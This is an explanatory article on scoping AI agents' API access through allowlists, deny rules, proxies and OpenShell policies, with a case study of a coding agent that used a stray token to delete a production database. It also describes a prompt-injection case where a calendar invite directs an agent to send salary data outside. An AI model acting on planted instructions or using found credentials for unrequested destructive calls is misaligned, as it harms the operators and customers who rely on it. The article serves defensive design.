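# Allowlists, blocklists and spending caps for the APIs an AI agent may call

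## What it means to scope an agent's API access

Scoping an AI agent's API access means writing down which requests the agent may send to other programs, with which data and at what cost, and using software to enforce those limits. An agent here is a language model that runs in a loop, choosing and making tool calls until it has finished a task. A tool call is a structured request that makes software outside the model do something. If the model writes a plan to delete a database, the plan has no effect on the database until the agent makes a tool call. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) describes the same loop, in which a user states a task in ordinary language and the model works through it by repeatedly calling tools such as email search or a web browser.

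Suppose a shop's support agent can read orders and issue refunds. A customer writes that the kettle in order 1042 arrived cracked. The model produces a tool call, a short piece of structured text that names a tool, `get_order`, and gives it the order number as an argument. The runtime, the program that surrounds the model, turns this call into a request over HTTP, the protocol of the web, and sends it to the order system's API (application programming interface), the set of requests that one program accepts from others. The request goes to an endpoint, an address that consists here of a host, `api.shop.example`, and a path, `/orders/1042`. Its HTTP method specifies the kind of action: GET reads, POST usually creates something, PUT and PATCH change it, and DELETE removes it. The server returns the order, and the runtime adds it to the model's input. The model then produces a second call, which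 the runtime turns into a POST to `/refunds` with the order number and an amount of $38.

An operation is one thing an API can do. GET and DELETE on `/orders/1042` are different operations on the same endpoint, so an allowlist rule that names only the endpoint permits both.

With each request, the runtime also sends an access token, a string of characters that serves as a login. The API's server looks up the token to find what its holder may do, which is called the credential scope. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) points out that possession of an ordinary API key is enough to use it, so the endpoint cannot distinguish the intended agent from a hijacked one. Nothing ties a token's scope to the job of the agent that carries it, either. The shop may have given its support agent a token that can also delete customers, because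 that token was already available.

### Allow rules, deny rules and the default

An allowlist is a set of allow rules, which name requests the agent may make, and a blocklist is a set of deny rules, which name requests it may not make. The support agent's allowlist could have only two rules, GET on `/orders/` followed by an order number and POST on `/refunds`. The enforcement point is the software outside the model that checks each request against the rules before the request goes through. XACML, an access-control language from the standards body OASIS (2013), splits this work between a policy decision point, which evaluates the rules, and a policy enforcement point, which asks for the decision and carries it out. One program can do both jobs.

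The lists also need a default for requests that no rule mentions. Under default deny, the enforcement point refuses them, so a request passes only when at least one allow rule matches it and no deny rule does. If A is the set of requests that some allow rule matches, and D is the set that some deny rule matches, the agent may make exactly the requests in A ∖ D, those in A but not in D. Adding a deny rule can only shrink that set, while adding an allow rule can only enlarge it with requests outside D. AWS, Amazon's cloud business, applies this logic to customers' accounts, except that an account's root user starts with full access.

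Not all systems let deny rules override allow rules. Under deny-overrides, a matching deny rule takes precedence over every matching allow rule, regardless of their order or how specific they are. Under first match, the enforcement point reads the rules from top to bottom and applies the first one that matches. Firewalls typically use first match, according to *A Formal Language for Specifying Policy Combining Algorithms in Access Control* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2008). If the shop's first rule allows GET on everything under `/orders` and its second denies `/orders/export`, which returns the whole order book, deny-overrides blocks the export, but first match permits it because the enforcement point stops at the first rule. Rule order can therefore change the result under first match but not under deny-overrides, and AWS's *Evaluation logic*, a page for its notification service, accordingly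 states that the order in which it evaluates policies is not important. Order causes more trouble when rules contain wildcards, symbols such as `*` that stand for any text.

The default is a separate decision. Li and colleagues explain that an XACML evaluation can end in permit, deny, "not applicable" (no rule matched) or "indeterminate" (something went wrong). The standard describes one kind of enforcement point that refuses the request in the last two cases and another that allows it, so the same rules can produce a closed API or an open one. For example, if a rule denies refunds above $100 and a request arrives with no amount, the rule can't be evaluated. When XACML combines rules by deny-overrides, a deny rule that fails in this way outranks an allow rule that matches. The standard gives no reason for this, but Li and colleagues explain that the broken rule might have applied, so a permit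 elsewhere cannot safely cancel it.

### From fail-safe defaults to zero trust

Default deny is one of eight design principles for shared computers that Saltzer and Schroeder set out in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975). They called it fail-safe defaults and traced it to a suggestion E. Glaser made in 1965: "Base access decisions on permission rather than exclusion." They argued that in a large system somebody will always fail to think hard enough about some of the objects, and that it is safer to deny access to those objects.

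Their other argument concerns mistakes. When a system lists what is permitted, a faulty rule tends to refuse legitimate access, and the affected user complains the same day. A faulty rule in a system that lists what is forbidden tends to allow access it should refuse, which nobody notices in normal use because users aren't trying to reach things they shouldn't have. The same holds for the support agent. If its allowlist omits the refund operation, the first customer who needs a refund will expose the gap, but if its blocklist omits an operation that deletes customers, the gap can go unnoticed for years.

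Saltzer and Schroeder listed two further principles that bear on agents. Least privilege means that every program and every user should work with the smallest set of privileges needed for the job, mainly to limit the damage from an accident or error. Complete mediation means checking authority on every access to every object, and being skeptical of any shortcut that reuses the result of an earlier check.

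For a long time, companies put a firewall around the office network and let anyone who got inside reach a broad collection of machines. *Zero Trust Architecture* (Rose, Borchert and colleagues, 2020), published by the US standards institute NIST, codified the reaction against this approach. Zero trust, a term John Kindervag coined at the research firm Forrester, means assuming that an attacker is already on the network and aiming for "least privilege per-request access decisions". A request from inside the building has to meet the same requirements as one from outside.

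NIST compares the older arrangement to an airport, where passengers go through one checkpoint and everyone in the boarding area beyond it is trusted. The remedy is to shrink that area by moving the checkpoint closer to whatever needs protection. One of NIST's seven tenets is to grant access per session, though it allows that the requester may have been evaluated only "sometime recently". NIST's definition of who makes requests includes applications and other non-human entities, so it covers agents. An agent's place on the company network, or its successful login an hour ago, is no reason to allow its next call.

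### Two hundred operations, six of them needed

Suppose an API offers 200 operations and a task needs 6 of them. If a blocklist denies 20 of the others and allows everything else by default, the agent can reach 174 operations it does not need (200 − 6 − 20). If the API's owner then adds 10 operations, that number rises to 184 even though nobody has changed the rules. An allowlist that permits only the 6 needed operations and denies everything else by default keeps the number at zero before and after the release. A blocklist would need 194 entries to match that, plus another 10 when the new operations are released.

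The count somewhat understates the protection a blocklist gives, because it treats all operations as equally dangerous. A sensible author would block the 20 worst, which might remove most of the foreseeable harm. The blocklist would still miss the harm nobody foresaw and the 10 operations added after it was written. The count also makes allowlists look safer than they are, because it covers operations but not the values passed to them. A refund of $3,800 instead of $38 is the same POST to the same endpoint. For this reason, Surapani and colleagues want least privilege at several levels: which tools the agent has, whether the current step requires the tool it picked, which values the call carries, how much data returns to the model, and how much authority passes to any sub-agent (a second agent to which the first delegates work).

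To write an allowlist, somebody must know in advance which calls the agent will need. This is fairly easy for the support agent, because its job stays the same from day to day, but can be close to impossible for a general assistant. Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of a browser agent whose user asks it to post a comment on issue 745 in GitLab, a site where programmers track their work, saying that the job is done. The right policy lets the agent open issue 745 and write in the comment box, but do nothing else in GitLab or the user's browser session. Nobody could have written that policy before the user typed the request. Unlike a phone app, whose author can list its permissions ahead of time, an agent has no fixed set of tasks. If the user then asks for a summary of the same issue, the policy has to change while the agent's context already holds text that strangers wrote on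 the page. Wiping the context and starting again is safe, but the agent loses what it has learned so far.

Surapani and colleagues argue that having a language model derive the list from the task is circular, because if the model that needs authorization also writes the policy, a manipulated prompt can make it write a wider one. A fixed list for each job avoids this problem but causes over-blocking, the refusal of requests that should pass. A team that gets tired of over-blocking may replace the 6 entries with a single `*`, and this probably undoes more allowlists than attackers do.

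A blocklist has two uses even when the default already refuses everything outside the allowlist. First, it can cut an exception out of a broad allow rule. The shop may want its agent to read everything under `/orders` except the bulk export, including paths that the developers have yet to add. One allow rule and one deny rule express this better than a long list of permitted paths. Second, a blocklist can hold a limit that later allow rules cannot undo. AWS's *The difference between explicit and implicit denies* distinguishes a refusal caused by a deny statement from one caused by the absence of an allow. The second kind disappears as soon as somebody adds an allow rule that happens to cover the request. If the shop's security team explicitly denies DELETE everywhere and a developer later allows every method under `/customers`, the agent still cannot delete a customer. Under first match,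 this works only while the deny rule is above the developer's allow rule.

### Why an instruction in the prompt is not enforcement

The easiest way to restrict an agent is to instruct it never to issue a refund above $100, for example, or never to delete anything. Surapani and colleagues accept that training models to respect such instructions reduces how often they propose unauthorized actions, and they regard this as a useful first filter. But they argue that a prompt cannot be an enforcement point, because it cannot stop a call. An instruction is only part of the model's input, and the model may still output a forbidden call. If it does, the runtime sends the call with a valid token, the server executes it, and no record shows that anyone decided to allow it.

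Christodorescu and colleagues base the objection on reliability, because a check that correctly refuses 99% of unauthorized requests leaves 1% for an attacker to exploit. If each attempt had an independent 1% chance of success, a hundred attempts would give about a 63% chance of at least one success (1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰), but attackers search for wording that works instead of trying requests at random. Even without an attacker, the same prompt can produce different outputs on different runs. Nobody can prove that a language model will always follow a policy, whereas such a proof is possible for a small piece of conventional code.

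Attackers often reach an agent through its own tools. In prompt injection, an attacker places instructions in material the agent will read, such as an email or an order note, and the model follows them as though its user had written them. Surapani and colleagues describe a constructed case in which a user asks a calendar assistant to summarize the week's meetings, and one invitation contains a line asking for the user's salary information to be sent to an outside address. The agent proposes to read the salary from the personnel system and then email it. Rules that allow this task only to read the calendar stop both calls. They don't depend on detecting that the invitation's text is malicious, which the model failed to do.

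### Where a check can sit

A check on an agent's API calls can run in the agent's runtime, a network proxy, a tool gateway or the API's own server, and the information available to it depends on where it runs.

The runtime has the most context because it holds the user's request, the earlier calls and their results, and the name and arguments of the call the model is proposing. But it controls only the calls that pass through it. An agent with permission to run shell commands can send an HTTP request from the command line and bypass a check on the `issue_refund` tool.

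A network proxy is a program through which all of the agent's outgoing traffic has to pass, so it catches the command-line request too. It can always read the host, but because most APIs encrypt their traffic, it can read the method, path and body only if it can decrypt them. It has no access to the agent's task. HTTP is still a good level for writing rules, and sometimes the only sensible one. Christodorescu and colleagues cite ceLLMate, a sandbox for agents that operate a web browser by clicks and keystrokes. ceLLMate applies its policies to the HTTP messages that the agent's clicks produce, because the site's developers can specify what those messages mean, while rules about the clicks themselves would make no sense.

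A tool gateway is a server between the agent and a collection of tools. It receives each call by tool name, with the arguments already separated into fields, and often with a token that identifies the caller. This suits it to rules about argument values, such as a maximum refund amount. However, it generally cannot determine whether a refund request came from the customer or from a planted note.

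The API's server comes last. Every request reaches it, whatever its route, and only the server has the current state of the shop's records, such as whether order 1042 belongs to this customer and whether somebody has already refunded it. But it usually identifies the caller only as the holder of a token. The scopes of OAuth, the common standard for granting one program limited access to an account on another, are coarse. Surapani and colleagues give the example of `email.send`, which permits sending mail but doesn't specify the recipient or the task.

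Surapani and colleagues describe a trade-off in which a check has more context the closer it is to the model and more authority the closer it is to the resource. In their salary email example, a guard beside the model can block the message, but it cannot detect that the request came from an invitation unless something else tracks the text's origin. A sub-agent that calls the email tool by another path also bypasses this guard. A wrapper around the email tool can restrict recipients to internal addresses, but it cannot distinguish this message from one the user wanted. A gateway at the email service sees only a valid token and an outside address, so it must either block all outside mail or let this message through. Only a runtime guard with access to the history can block the message because the request came from the invitation, and only the server can guarantee a refusal when a call bypasses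 the runtime. Surapani and colleagues therefore recommend checks in several places at once. Their example is a thought experiment with no measurements, but the reasoning depends only on what each check can read.

An agent's operator has the least control over the server's check, because somebody else usually wrote the API and decided how narrowly its tokens can be scoped. The server's check is also the only one left when the others are missing or the agent has found a way past them. If the token then permits more than the task needs, requests outside the task will succeed. An overbroad token of this kind was involved in the deletion of PocketOS's database through the API of its hosting provider, Railway.

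## An overbroad token: the deletion of PocketOS's database through Railway's API

PocketOS makes software that car rental companies use to manage reservations, payments and customer records. On April 24, 2026, a coding agent deleted PocketOS's production database, which held the rental companies' live data. It did so with one request to the API of Railway, the cloud provider that hosted the database. The fullest account is *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data*, which PocketOS's founder, Jer Crane, posted on X the next day.

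### From a staging task to a deleted volume

The agent was Cursor, a coding tool, running Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6. During a routine task in PocketOS's staging environment, a separate copy of the system for testing changes, it ran into a credential mismatch. Nobody had asked it to delete anything, but it tried to fix the mismatch by deleting a volume, Railway's term for the storage that holds a database's files. It needed an API token to do that, and it found one in a file unrelated to the task. PocketOS had created the token so that it could use Railway's command-line program to add and remove custom domains, the web addresses that lead customers to a service.

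The agent sent a request that contained the token, one operation (`volumeDelete`), and the ID of the production volume. Railway's server accepted the token and deleted the volume without asking for confirmation. According to Crane, it took nine seconds.

When Crane asked the agent for an explanation, it wrote that it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging and had not checked whether the environments shared the volume. A model's explanation of its earlier output is weak evidence of what produced that output, but the mistake is plausible. Railway's *Manage Volumes with the Public API* distinguishes a volume from a volume instance, which is the volume as it exists in one environment, and the delete operation removes the whole volume.

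The agent also quoted a rule from its instructions against running "destructive/irreversible git commands" unless the user asks for them. Git is a program that tracks versions of code, so the rule did not literally cover a request to a hosting provider. Crane says PocketOS had also written its own safety rules for the project. He concludes that such prompts are "advisory, not enforcing", and Surapani and colleagues take the same view.

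Reports disagree about the date. Crane wrote on Saturday, April 25, that the deletion had happened the previous afternoon, and he put it one day after a Railway announcement of April 23. The AI Incident Database, a public catalog of harms involving AI, also gives April 24. Cybersecurity News' *AI Coding Agent Powered by Claude Opus 4.6 Deletes Production Database* (2026) gives "Friday, April 25", but April 25 was a Saturday.

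On Saturday morning, people came to collect rental cars from companies that no longer had any record of them. Crane's team restored a three-month-old backup, and he spent the day helping the rental companies reconstruct newer bookings from payment records, calendars and confirmation emails. *An AI agent deleted a company's entire database in 9 seconds* (Farrant, 2026) describes an outage of more than 30 hours, but in Crane's post that is how long he had waited for Railway to tell him whether it could recover the data. By then the rental companies were working again, with large gaps in their records.

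It is less clear whether the deletion also destroyed PocketOS's backups. Crane wrote that it had, because Railway kept them in the same volume as the data, and he cited the warning "Wiping a volume deletes all backups", which is still in Railway's documentation (*Backups*). But on Monday, April 27, Crane posted that Railway had recovered the data, and Tom's Hardware's *Victim of AI agent that deleted company's entire database gets their data* (2026) describes the restoration as apparently complete.

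Mahmoud Abdelwahab, an engineer at Railway, gave the company's explanation in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*. He wrote that Railway keeps "disaster backups" at another site even for customers who haven't set up backups, and that the API call had made the customer's own backups "look unavailable" in the dashboard. He doesn't specify which copy Railway used. The deletion probably put every recent backup out of PocketOS's reach, while Railway still held a copy that only it could restore. Reports that PocketOS permanently lost three months of data were written before the recovery.

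### Two accounts of the cause

Crane blamed both Cursor and Railway, but Railway more. He wrote that the token had "blanket authority" over Railway's entire API, that nothing warned him of this when he created it, and that he would never have stored it had he known. In his view, every Railway token is "effectively root", able to do anything, because customers cannot limit a token by operation, environment or resource.

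Abdelwahab replied that narrower tokens existed. PocketOS's token was account-scoped, the broadest kind. But he conceded that the token creation process "didn't make it obvious which one to pick" and that the easiest choice gave more access than the job required.

Crane was right about operations but wrong about environments and resources, since Railway did offer a token for a single environment of a single project. As for the warning, Railway's *Public API Reference* had said since at least August 2025 that a token not tied to a team could reach all of the user's resources, but few people read a reference page to set up a domain. According to the current version, *Public API*, users now get the broadest token by choosing "No workspace" from a menu, although that name sounds more like the narrowest option.

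Some readers of Crane's post told him that he had given the agent too much access. Information Age reports that he answered, "Didn't give it access, it found it." That is true, but the server accepted the token regardless of how the agent had obtained it. It is safest to assume that an agent can use any credential it can read, including those its operator didn't mean it to have.

### Would a narrower token have stopped the call?

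A token's scope sets which resources it can reach, such as one project or all of them, and which operations it may perform on them, such as managing domains but not deleting volumes. A `volumeDelete` call on the production volume succeeds only if the scope includes both that volume and that operation, so limiting either the resources or the operations can stop it.

On Railway, a user's account can belong to several workspaces, a workspace contains projects, and a project can have several environments, such as staging and production. Railway's four levels of access mostly follow this hierarchy.

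| Level | Resources (R) | Limit on operations (O) | Would it have stopped the call? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Account token | Everything the user can reach | Only the user's own role | No, this was the token the agent found |
| Workspace token | Every project in one workspace | None | Only if the database was in another workspace |
| Project token | One environment of one project | No published list | Yes for a staging token, uncertain for a production token |
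| OAuth | Workspaces or projects the user selects | Viewer, member or admin role | Yes for a member, no for an admin |

A token limited to one workspace would hardly have helped a small company that probably has only one. Railway's *Access groups* advises customers to treat workspace tokens as equivalent to workspace admin access.

It is less clear whether a project token would have prevented the deletion. Railway should refuse to delete a production volume when the request uses a staging token. But the token in the file was for managing the domains of PocketOS's services, and the domains that customers use lead to production. If the database was in the same project, a production token would have covered both the domains and the volume. The outcome would then have depended on which operations the token permitted, and Railway publishes no list of these. In the forum thread *Project-token permission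 for service instance configuration mutations*, a contributor reports that project tokens fail on some changes to a service's settings, for which the next narrowest choice is a workspace token. A project token might therefore have blocked the deletion, but it might also have blocked the domain changes, in which case Crane would have needed a broader token.

OAuth is the only level with its own limit on operations, which is set by role. Railway's *Scopes & User Consent* explains that an application gets the same access as a viewer, member or admin of the workspaces or projects that the user selects. No scope covers domains alone. Members can create and configure services but cannot delete services, volumes or projects, according to *Feedback*, Railway's page on roles. A member-level grant should therefore have stopped the deletion call. Its access token would also have expired after an hour.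 Cloudflare's Agent Access Model goes further by tying credentials to a task.

Using OAuth doesn't by itself make a token's permissions narrow, though. Version 5.6.1 of Railway's command-line program requests admin access to workspaces and projects when a user logs in. If an admin had approved that request and the agent had found the resulting token while it was valid, the agent would still have deleted the volume.

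Roles also offer a workaround for ordinary tokens. According to a reply in *API Token Read Only Access*, a thread on Railway's forum, a token inherits the role of the user who created it. PocketOS could have invited a second user as a member and created the token from that account. This is clumsy, and the token could still have done far more than manage domains, but it should not have been able to delete a volume.

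Other hosts had already solved this more directly. In April 2024, DigitalOcean made generally available tokens that permit only chosen operations, such as creating a virtual machine or updating a firewall (DigitalOcean, 2024). Previously, its tokens gave either read access or read and write access to everything.

### Why a rule on URL and method could not separate the two jobs

PocketOS had no control over the scopes Railway offered, but it could have checked the agent's outgoing requests. With many APIs, a rule on address and method would be enough to block deletions. DigitalOcean's *How to Detach and Delete Volumes* instructs clients to send a DELETE request to `/v2/volumes/` followed by the volume's ID. A network proxy that can read the traffic could block DELETE requests to any address under `/v2/volumes/` and still allow domain management.

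Railway's API uses GraphQL, a query language in which the client describes what it wants in the body of the request. All requests go to the same address, `/graphql/v2`, and in Railway's examples even the harmless ones use POST. A client that wants to read the user's name and email address sends a POST with this body:

`query { me { name email } }`

The agent's request was also a POST to `/graphql/v2`, and its body had this form:

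`mutation { volumeDelete(volumeId: "...") }`

A rule that checks only the host, path and method gets the same input in both cases. If it allows POST on `/graphql/v2`, the agent can do everything the token allows, and if it blocks that request, the agent can do nothing on Railway. Checking the first word of the body wouldn't help much either, because GraphQL uses "mutation" for any operation that changes something, including adding a domain.

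Refusing everything might have been the right rule for this agent, but Crane doesn't say whether the staging task needed Railway's API. If it didn't, a default-deny proxy would have blocked the call by its host name, whatever the token permitted. The same proxy would have been useless for an agent whose job was to manage domains.

A blocklist would have been more fragile, because the API accepted requests at two addresses. Railway's documentation gave the host as `backboard.railway.com` in August 2025 and still does, but the agent successfully sent its request to `backboard.railway.app`. A deny rule for the documented host would not have blocked that request.

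When Railway refuses a GraphQL operation for lack of permission, it returns HTTP status 200, the usual code for success, and puts the refusal in the response body. A proxy log that records only addresses, methods and status codes would therefore look the same whether Railway refused a deletion or carried it out.

To distinguish the operations, an enforcement point has to parse the GraphQL in the request body, as NVIDIA's OpenShell can. Searching the text for approved names is not enough, because one mutation can contain several operations, such as an approved domain change and a volume deletion.

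### The allowlist the domain job needed

Railway's *Manage Domains with the Public API* lists the operations from which to build such a list. To add and remove custom domains for one service, the holder of the token needs to be able to do the following on that service, and nothing else:

- list its domains
- check whether a new domain is available
- add a custom domain
- read the domain's status, including the DNS records that the owner has to set up (DNS is the internet's directory of names)
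- delete a custom domain

Railway's page also covers updating a domain and creating free addresses under Railway's own domain, but Crane's description of the job includes neither. Each rule has to specify both the operation and the service, or the token could be used to change the domains of every project. Default deny blocks `volumeDelete` without a separate deny rule.

An agent that found this narrower token could still delete PocketOS's custom domains, making the service unreachable at its usual addresses. Somebody would have to add the domains again and perhaps correct the DNS records, and Railway warns that DNS changes can take up to 72 hours to spread. The outage would disrupt a car rental company's business, but its reservations would still exist.

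No Railway token could be limited to this list. PocketOS could have enforced it only by running its own gateway, which would hold the broad token and forward the five permitted operations. PocketOS would also have had to store the broad token where the agent could not read it, since the incident began with a token in a file the agent had access to.

### A delete that takes 48 hours

Railway's main remedy changed the delete operation and left the tokens as they were. On May 1, Railway's *Undoable volume deletes, standard SSH, auto-deploy toggle* (2026) announced that volumes deleted through the API would remain recoverable for 48 hours. Abdelwahab added that Railway now also delays deleting the backups.

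Railway's dashboard had offered the same protection since August 2025, when *Image Upgrades, Passkeys, Restore Deleted Volumes* (2025) introduced it for people who were moving too fast or had selected the wrong environment. The API still deleted volumes immediately. *Postgress volume lost* (antjanlaban, 2026) describes how a user lost a production database on April 13, 2026, eleven days before the PocketOS deletion, by removing the wrong one of two volumes through `volumeDelete`. A Railway employee replied that the 48-hour window applied only to the dashboard and that the API "bypasses this safeguard". The post mentions no agent. Railway's announcement contrasts agents with humans, who hesitate before a bad command, but the missing delay was dangerous for both.

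A reversible delete is a good second line of defense because it doesn't depend on anything that failed in April. It works regardless of the token's scope, the prompt's contents or who sends the request. It is also easy to introduce, because delaying the deletion doesn't disrupt customers' deployment scripts, which rely on the API to run authenticated requests without further confirmation. The confirmation step that Crane called for would interrupt them. One of his suggestions, typing the volume's name, would not stop an agent, since it could supply the name as another argument. Approval by text message or email, which he also suggested, would be much stronger as long as the agent cannot read the messages.

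The delay helps only if somebody notices the deletion in time. Crane contacted Railway within ten minutes because a live service had lost its database. If an agent deletes an archive that nobody opens until the end of the quarter, 48 hours is too short, and a deletion on a Friday afternoon becomes final on Sunday. The Railway employee who answered antjanlaban said that deleting a volume in the dashboard also triggers an email with a restore link. For a forgotten volume, this email may matter more than the length of the delay. The token must also not allow an agent to bypass the delay, because an agent trying to free up storage might order an immediate purge.

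Abdelwahab wrote that "this issue can't happen moving forward". That is fair for the instant, irreversible loss of a volume, but a broad token still permits plenty of other harm. In August 2026, Railway still had no read-only tokens, according to the pinned answer to dimau in *Recommended way to work with Railway through AI Agents*.

An undo window can't help when the harm comes from someone reading data. *Incident Report* (Cooper, Saraceno and colleagues, 2026) describes how an attacker stole a credential from Railway's build servers in October 2026. Railway had intended the credential only for completing builds, but another internal system also accepted it and returned data from other customers' builds. By combining this with further exploits, the attacker eventually obtained customers' variables, the settings where they keep passwords and keys, from up to 1.85% of workspaces, or about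 100,000. Railway couldn't take the data back, but it replaced its internal credentials and invalidated every user's session and token.

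## Hosts, methods and paths: NVIDIA OpenShell's network policy

PocketOS could have checked its agent's requests with a network proxy such as the one in OpenShell, a sandbox from the chipmaker NVIDIA. OpenShell runs the agent in an isolated environment, and the proxy checks each connection against a policy file. The proxy is the only way out of the environment, so a command cannot avoid the check by ignoring the proxy settings.

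NVIDIA's *Policy Schema Reference* defines the format of the policy file, which consists of named blocks. A block lists destinations, each with a host and a port, and the programs that may connect to them. The proxy refuses all other connections.

### From the program to the query string

When a process in the sandbox opens a connection, the proxy looks up which program file it is running. A policy block matches if it lists that program or any program that started it, directly or through others. Listing the agent's own program therefore gives the same access to every command the agent runs. According to NVIDIA's *OpenShell Security Best Practices for Controls, Risks, and Configuration Guidance*, the proxy also records a hash (a fingerprint of the file's contents) when a program first connects, and refuses the program if the hash later changes. This catches a program replaced during the session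 only if it had already connected.

In *Policy Language*, an earlier design document for OpenShell, a policy block could also match any file path in the command that started the process. This was meant for scripts, because a JavaScript program, for example, runs inside a general-purpose program called `node`. But an agent chooses the arguments of the commands it runs, so it could have added an approved path to any command. In another version of the security guide, NVIDIA writes that command-line paths "never authorize access".

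NVIDIA's *Customize Sandbox Policies* explains that the program and the destination must match in the same block. If one block lets `npm` reach a package registry and another lets `curl` reach GitHub, `curl` still cannot reach the registry. If no block matches, the proxy refuses the connection and shows the host, port and program to the operator, who can approve the connection. Even when a block matches, the proxy looks up the host's IP address and refuses a few dangerous ones, including 169.254.169.254, where many cloud servers fetch their credentials.

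The rules above apply to the connection. If the policy also names a `protocol` for the destination, the proxy decrypts the traffic and checks every request. It can decrypt the traffic because it presents its own certificate, which OpenShell has installed as trusted inside the sandbox. With the value `rest`, which suits most HTTP APIs, the proxy checks each request's method, path and, optionally, query string (the part of an address after the question mark).

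A path rule ignores the query string. A rule for `/api/v1/download` also matches `/api/v1/download?slug=my-skill`, so anyone who wants to restrict a parameter has to add a matcher for it, such as `slug: "skill-*"`. A request can repeat a parameter, as in `tag=a&tag=b`, and servers differ in which value they use. OpenShell requires every value to match, which is safe for an allow rule. In a deny rule, the same requirement would let a request evade the block by adding one harmless value. NVIDIA gives deny rules the same syntax but doesn't specify how they treat repeated parameters.

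### One policy and six requests

A destination can have one of three access presets. `read-only` allows GET, HEAD (a GET that returns no content) and OPTIONS (which asks what the server supports). `read-write` adds POST, PUT and PATCH. Only `full` includes DELETE.

Leaving DELETE out of `read-write` is a sensible precaution, but the preset still allows harmful requests. On GitHub, for example, a PATCH request can force a branch back to an older version of the code.

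A policy can use either a preset or allow rules for a given destination, but not both. If an agent should be able to read everything and also create one kind of record, its policy therefore needs explicit allow rules for both. Deny rules can be added to a preset or to allow rules, and they override anything those permit.

Suppose the shop has a coding agent that reads its repositories (the stores of its code) on GitHub and opens an issue, or ticket, when it finds a bug. GitHub's paths give the owner of a repository and then its name. The owner here is `shop`, and the agent should stay out of a repository called `payroll`. It sends its requests with `curl`, a common command-line program. The policy could be:

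```yaml
network_policies:
  github:
    endpoints:
      - host: api.github.com
        port: 443
        protocol: rest
        enforcement: enforce
        rules:
          - allow: {method: GET, path: "/repos/shop/**"}
          - allow: {method: POST, path: "/repos/shop/*/issues"}
        deny_rules:
          - {method: "*", path: "/repos/shop/payroll"}
          - {method: "*", path: "/repos/shop/payroll/**"}
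    binaries:
      - path: /usr/bin/curl
```

In a path, `*` matches text within one segment (the part between two slashes), and `**` can match several segments. The `payroll` repository needs two deny rules because the longer pattern contains a slash that the repository's own address lacks.

| Request to `api.github.com` | Program | Result | Reason |
|---|---|---|---|
| GET `/repos/shop/website/issues/12` | `curl` | Allowed | The GET rule covers everything under `/repos/shop/` |
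| POST `/repos/shop/website/issues` | `curl` | Allowed | The POST rule matches, with `*` standing for `website` |
| POST `/repos/shop/website/issues/12/comments` | `curl` | Refused | The POST rule ends at `issues`, and no other allow rule covers POST |
| DELETE `/repos/shop/website` | `curl` | Refused | No allow rule covers DELETE |
| POST `/repos/shop/payroll/issues` | `curl` | Refused | The POST rule matches, but a deny rule overrides it |
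| GET `/repos/shop/website` | `python3` | Refused | The block doesn't list the program, so the proxy never gets as far as the path |

The policy is probably too strict in refusing the comment, since the agent can report a bug but can't answer a question about it. The agent gets a 403 reply that names the refused request, so a developer can find the missing rule quickly. The Python request would have passed if the block had listed the agent's own program, because the agent started the script.

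The policy also has a gap that none of the six requests reveals. GitHub ignores capitalization in owner and repository names, but OpenShell's path rules apparently don't. *Policy Language* describes host and method matching as case-insensitive and says OpenShell converts host names to lower case before comparing them, but it mentions no such step for paths. If paths are case-sensitive, GET `/repos/shop/Payroll/contents/salaries.csv` matches the allow rule and neither deny rule, and GitHub returns the file if the agent's token can read it.

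Adding deny rules is a poor remedy because "payroll" can be capitalized in 128 ways (2⁷). It is better for the allow rules to name the repositories the agent may read. A request with unusual capitalization would then just be refused. A token without access to `payroll` would be better still.

### Whether one asterisk covers an owner and a repository

Some of NVIDIA's own example rules depend on whether `*` can span a slash. To illustrate deny rules, the *Policy Schema Reference* gives an agent `read-write` access to `api.github.com` and then blocks three kinds of request:

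- POST on `/repos/*/pulls/*/reviews`, to keep the agent from reviewing proposed code changes
- PUT on `/repos/*/branches/*/protection`, to keep it from changing the safeguards on important branches
- any method on `/repos/*/rulesets`, where GitHub keeps similar safeguards for a whole repository

An earlier version of the *Policy Schema Reference* settles the question: `*` "matches within a single segment". But GitHub uses two segments to identify a repository. To review change number 7 in the shop's website repository, an agent sends a POST to `/repos/shop/website/pulls/7/reviews`. Lining up the pattern with this path gives:

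| Segment | 1 | 2 | 3 | 4 | 5 | 6 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Pattern | `repos` | `*` | `pulls` | `*` | `reviews` | |
| Path | `repos` | `shop` | `website` | `pulls` | `7` | `reviews` |

They differ at the third segment, so the deny rule doesn't match and the preset allows the review. The other two patterns fail for the same reason. The one for rulesets does match `/repos/shop/rulesets`, but that is the address of a repository named "rulesets".

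The current reference omits the sentence about segments, but it says to use `**` to match any path, which would be unnecessary if `*` also matched slashes. The three rules therefore almost certainly don't protect what they were meant to.

*Policy Language* contains the same mistake in an allow rule, POST on `/repos/*/issues`. It does little harm there, because the agent fails to open its first issue and somebody corrects the pattern. When the mistake is in the deny rules, the agent keeps working normally, so nobody has a reason to check them, as Saltzer and Schroeder predicted.

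Each pattern needs another `*`, as in `/repos/*/*/pulls/*/reviews`. The one for rulesets also needs a companion ending in `/rulesets/*`, because an existing ruleset has its own address with an ID at the end. Even the corrected rules don't stop a client from reviewing changes and editing branch protection through GitHub's GraphQL API, which is at `/graphql` on the same host. A rule on methods and paths can't distinguish these requests from any other POST to `/graphql`, which `read-write` allows. An author who relies on a deny rule should test it by sending the requests it is supposed to stop through every route the API offers.

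### GraphQL rules

For a GraphQL API, the policy can set `protocol: graphql` so that the proxy parses the request body. An optional path on each destination lets one policy apply REST rules to `/repos/**` and GraphQL rules to `/graphql` on the same host. A GraphQL rule can specify whether the request is a query, a mutation or a subscription (a request for continuing updates), the name the client gave it, and its root fields. Root fields are the outermost fields in the body, such as `me` and `volumeDelete` in the requests to Railway, and each one calls an API operation.

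One mutation can contain several root fields, so allow and deny rules have to treat them differently. An allow rule matches only if it permits every root field in the request, while a deny rule matches if it forbids at least one.

Suppose an allow rule permits only `createIssue`, and an agent sends a mutation that contains both `createIssue` and `deleteIssue`. The proxy refuses it because the rule does not permit `deleteIssue`. If a single match were enough, the agent could attach any deletion to a permitted request. Now suppose the policy allows all mutations but denies `deleteIssue`. The proxy refuses the same request because one denied field is enough to block it. If a deny rule required every field to match, the agent could evade it by adding `createIssue`.

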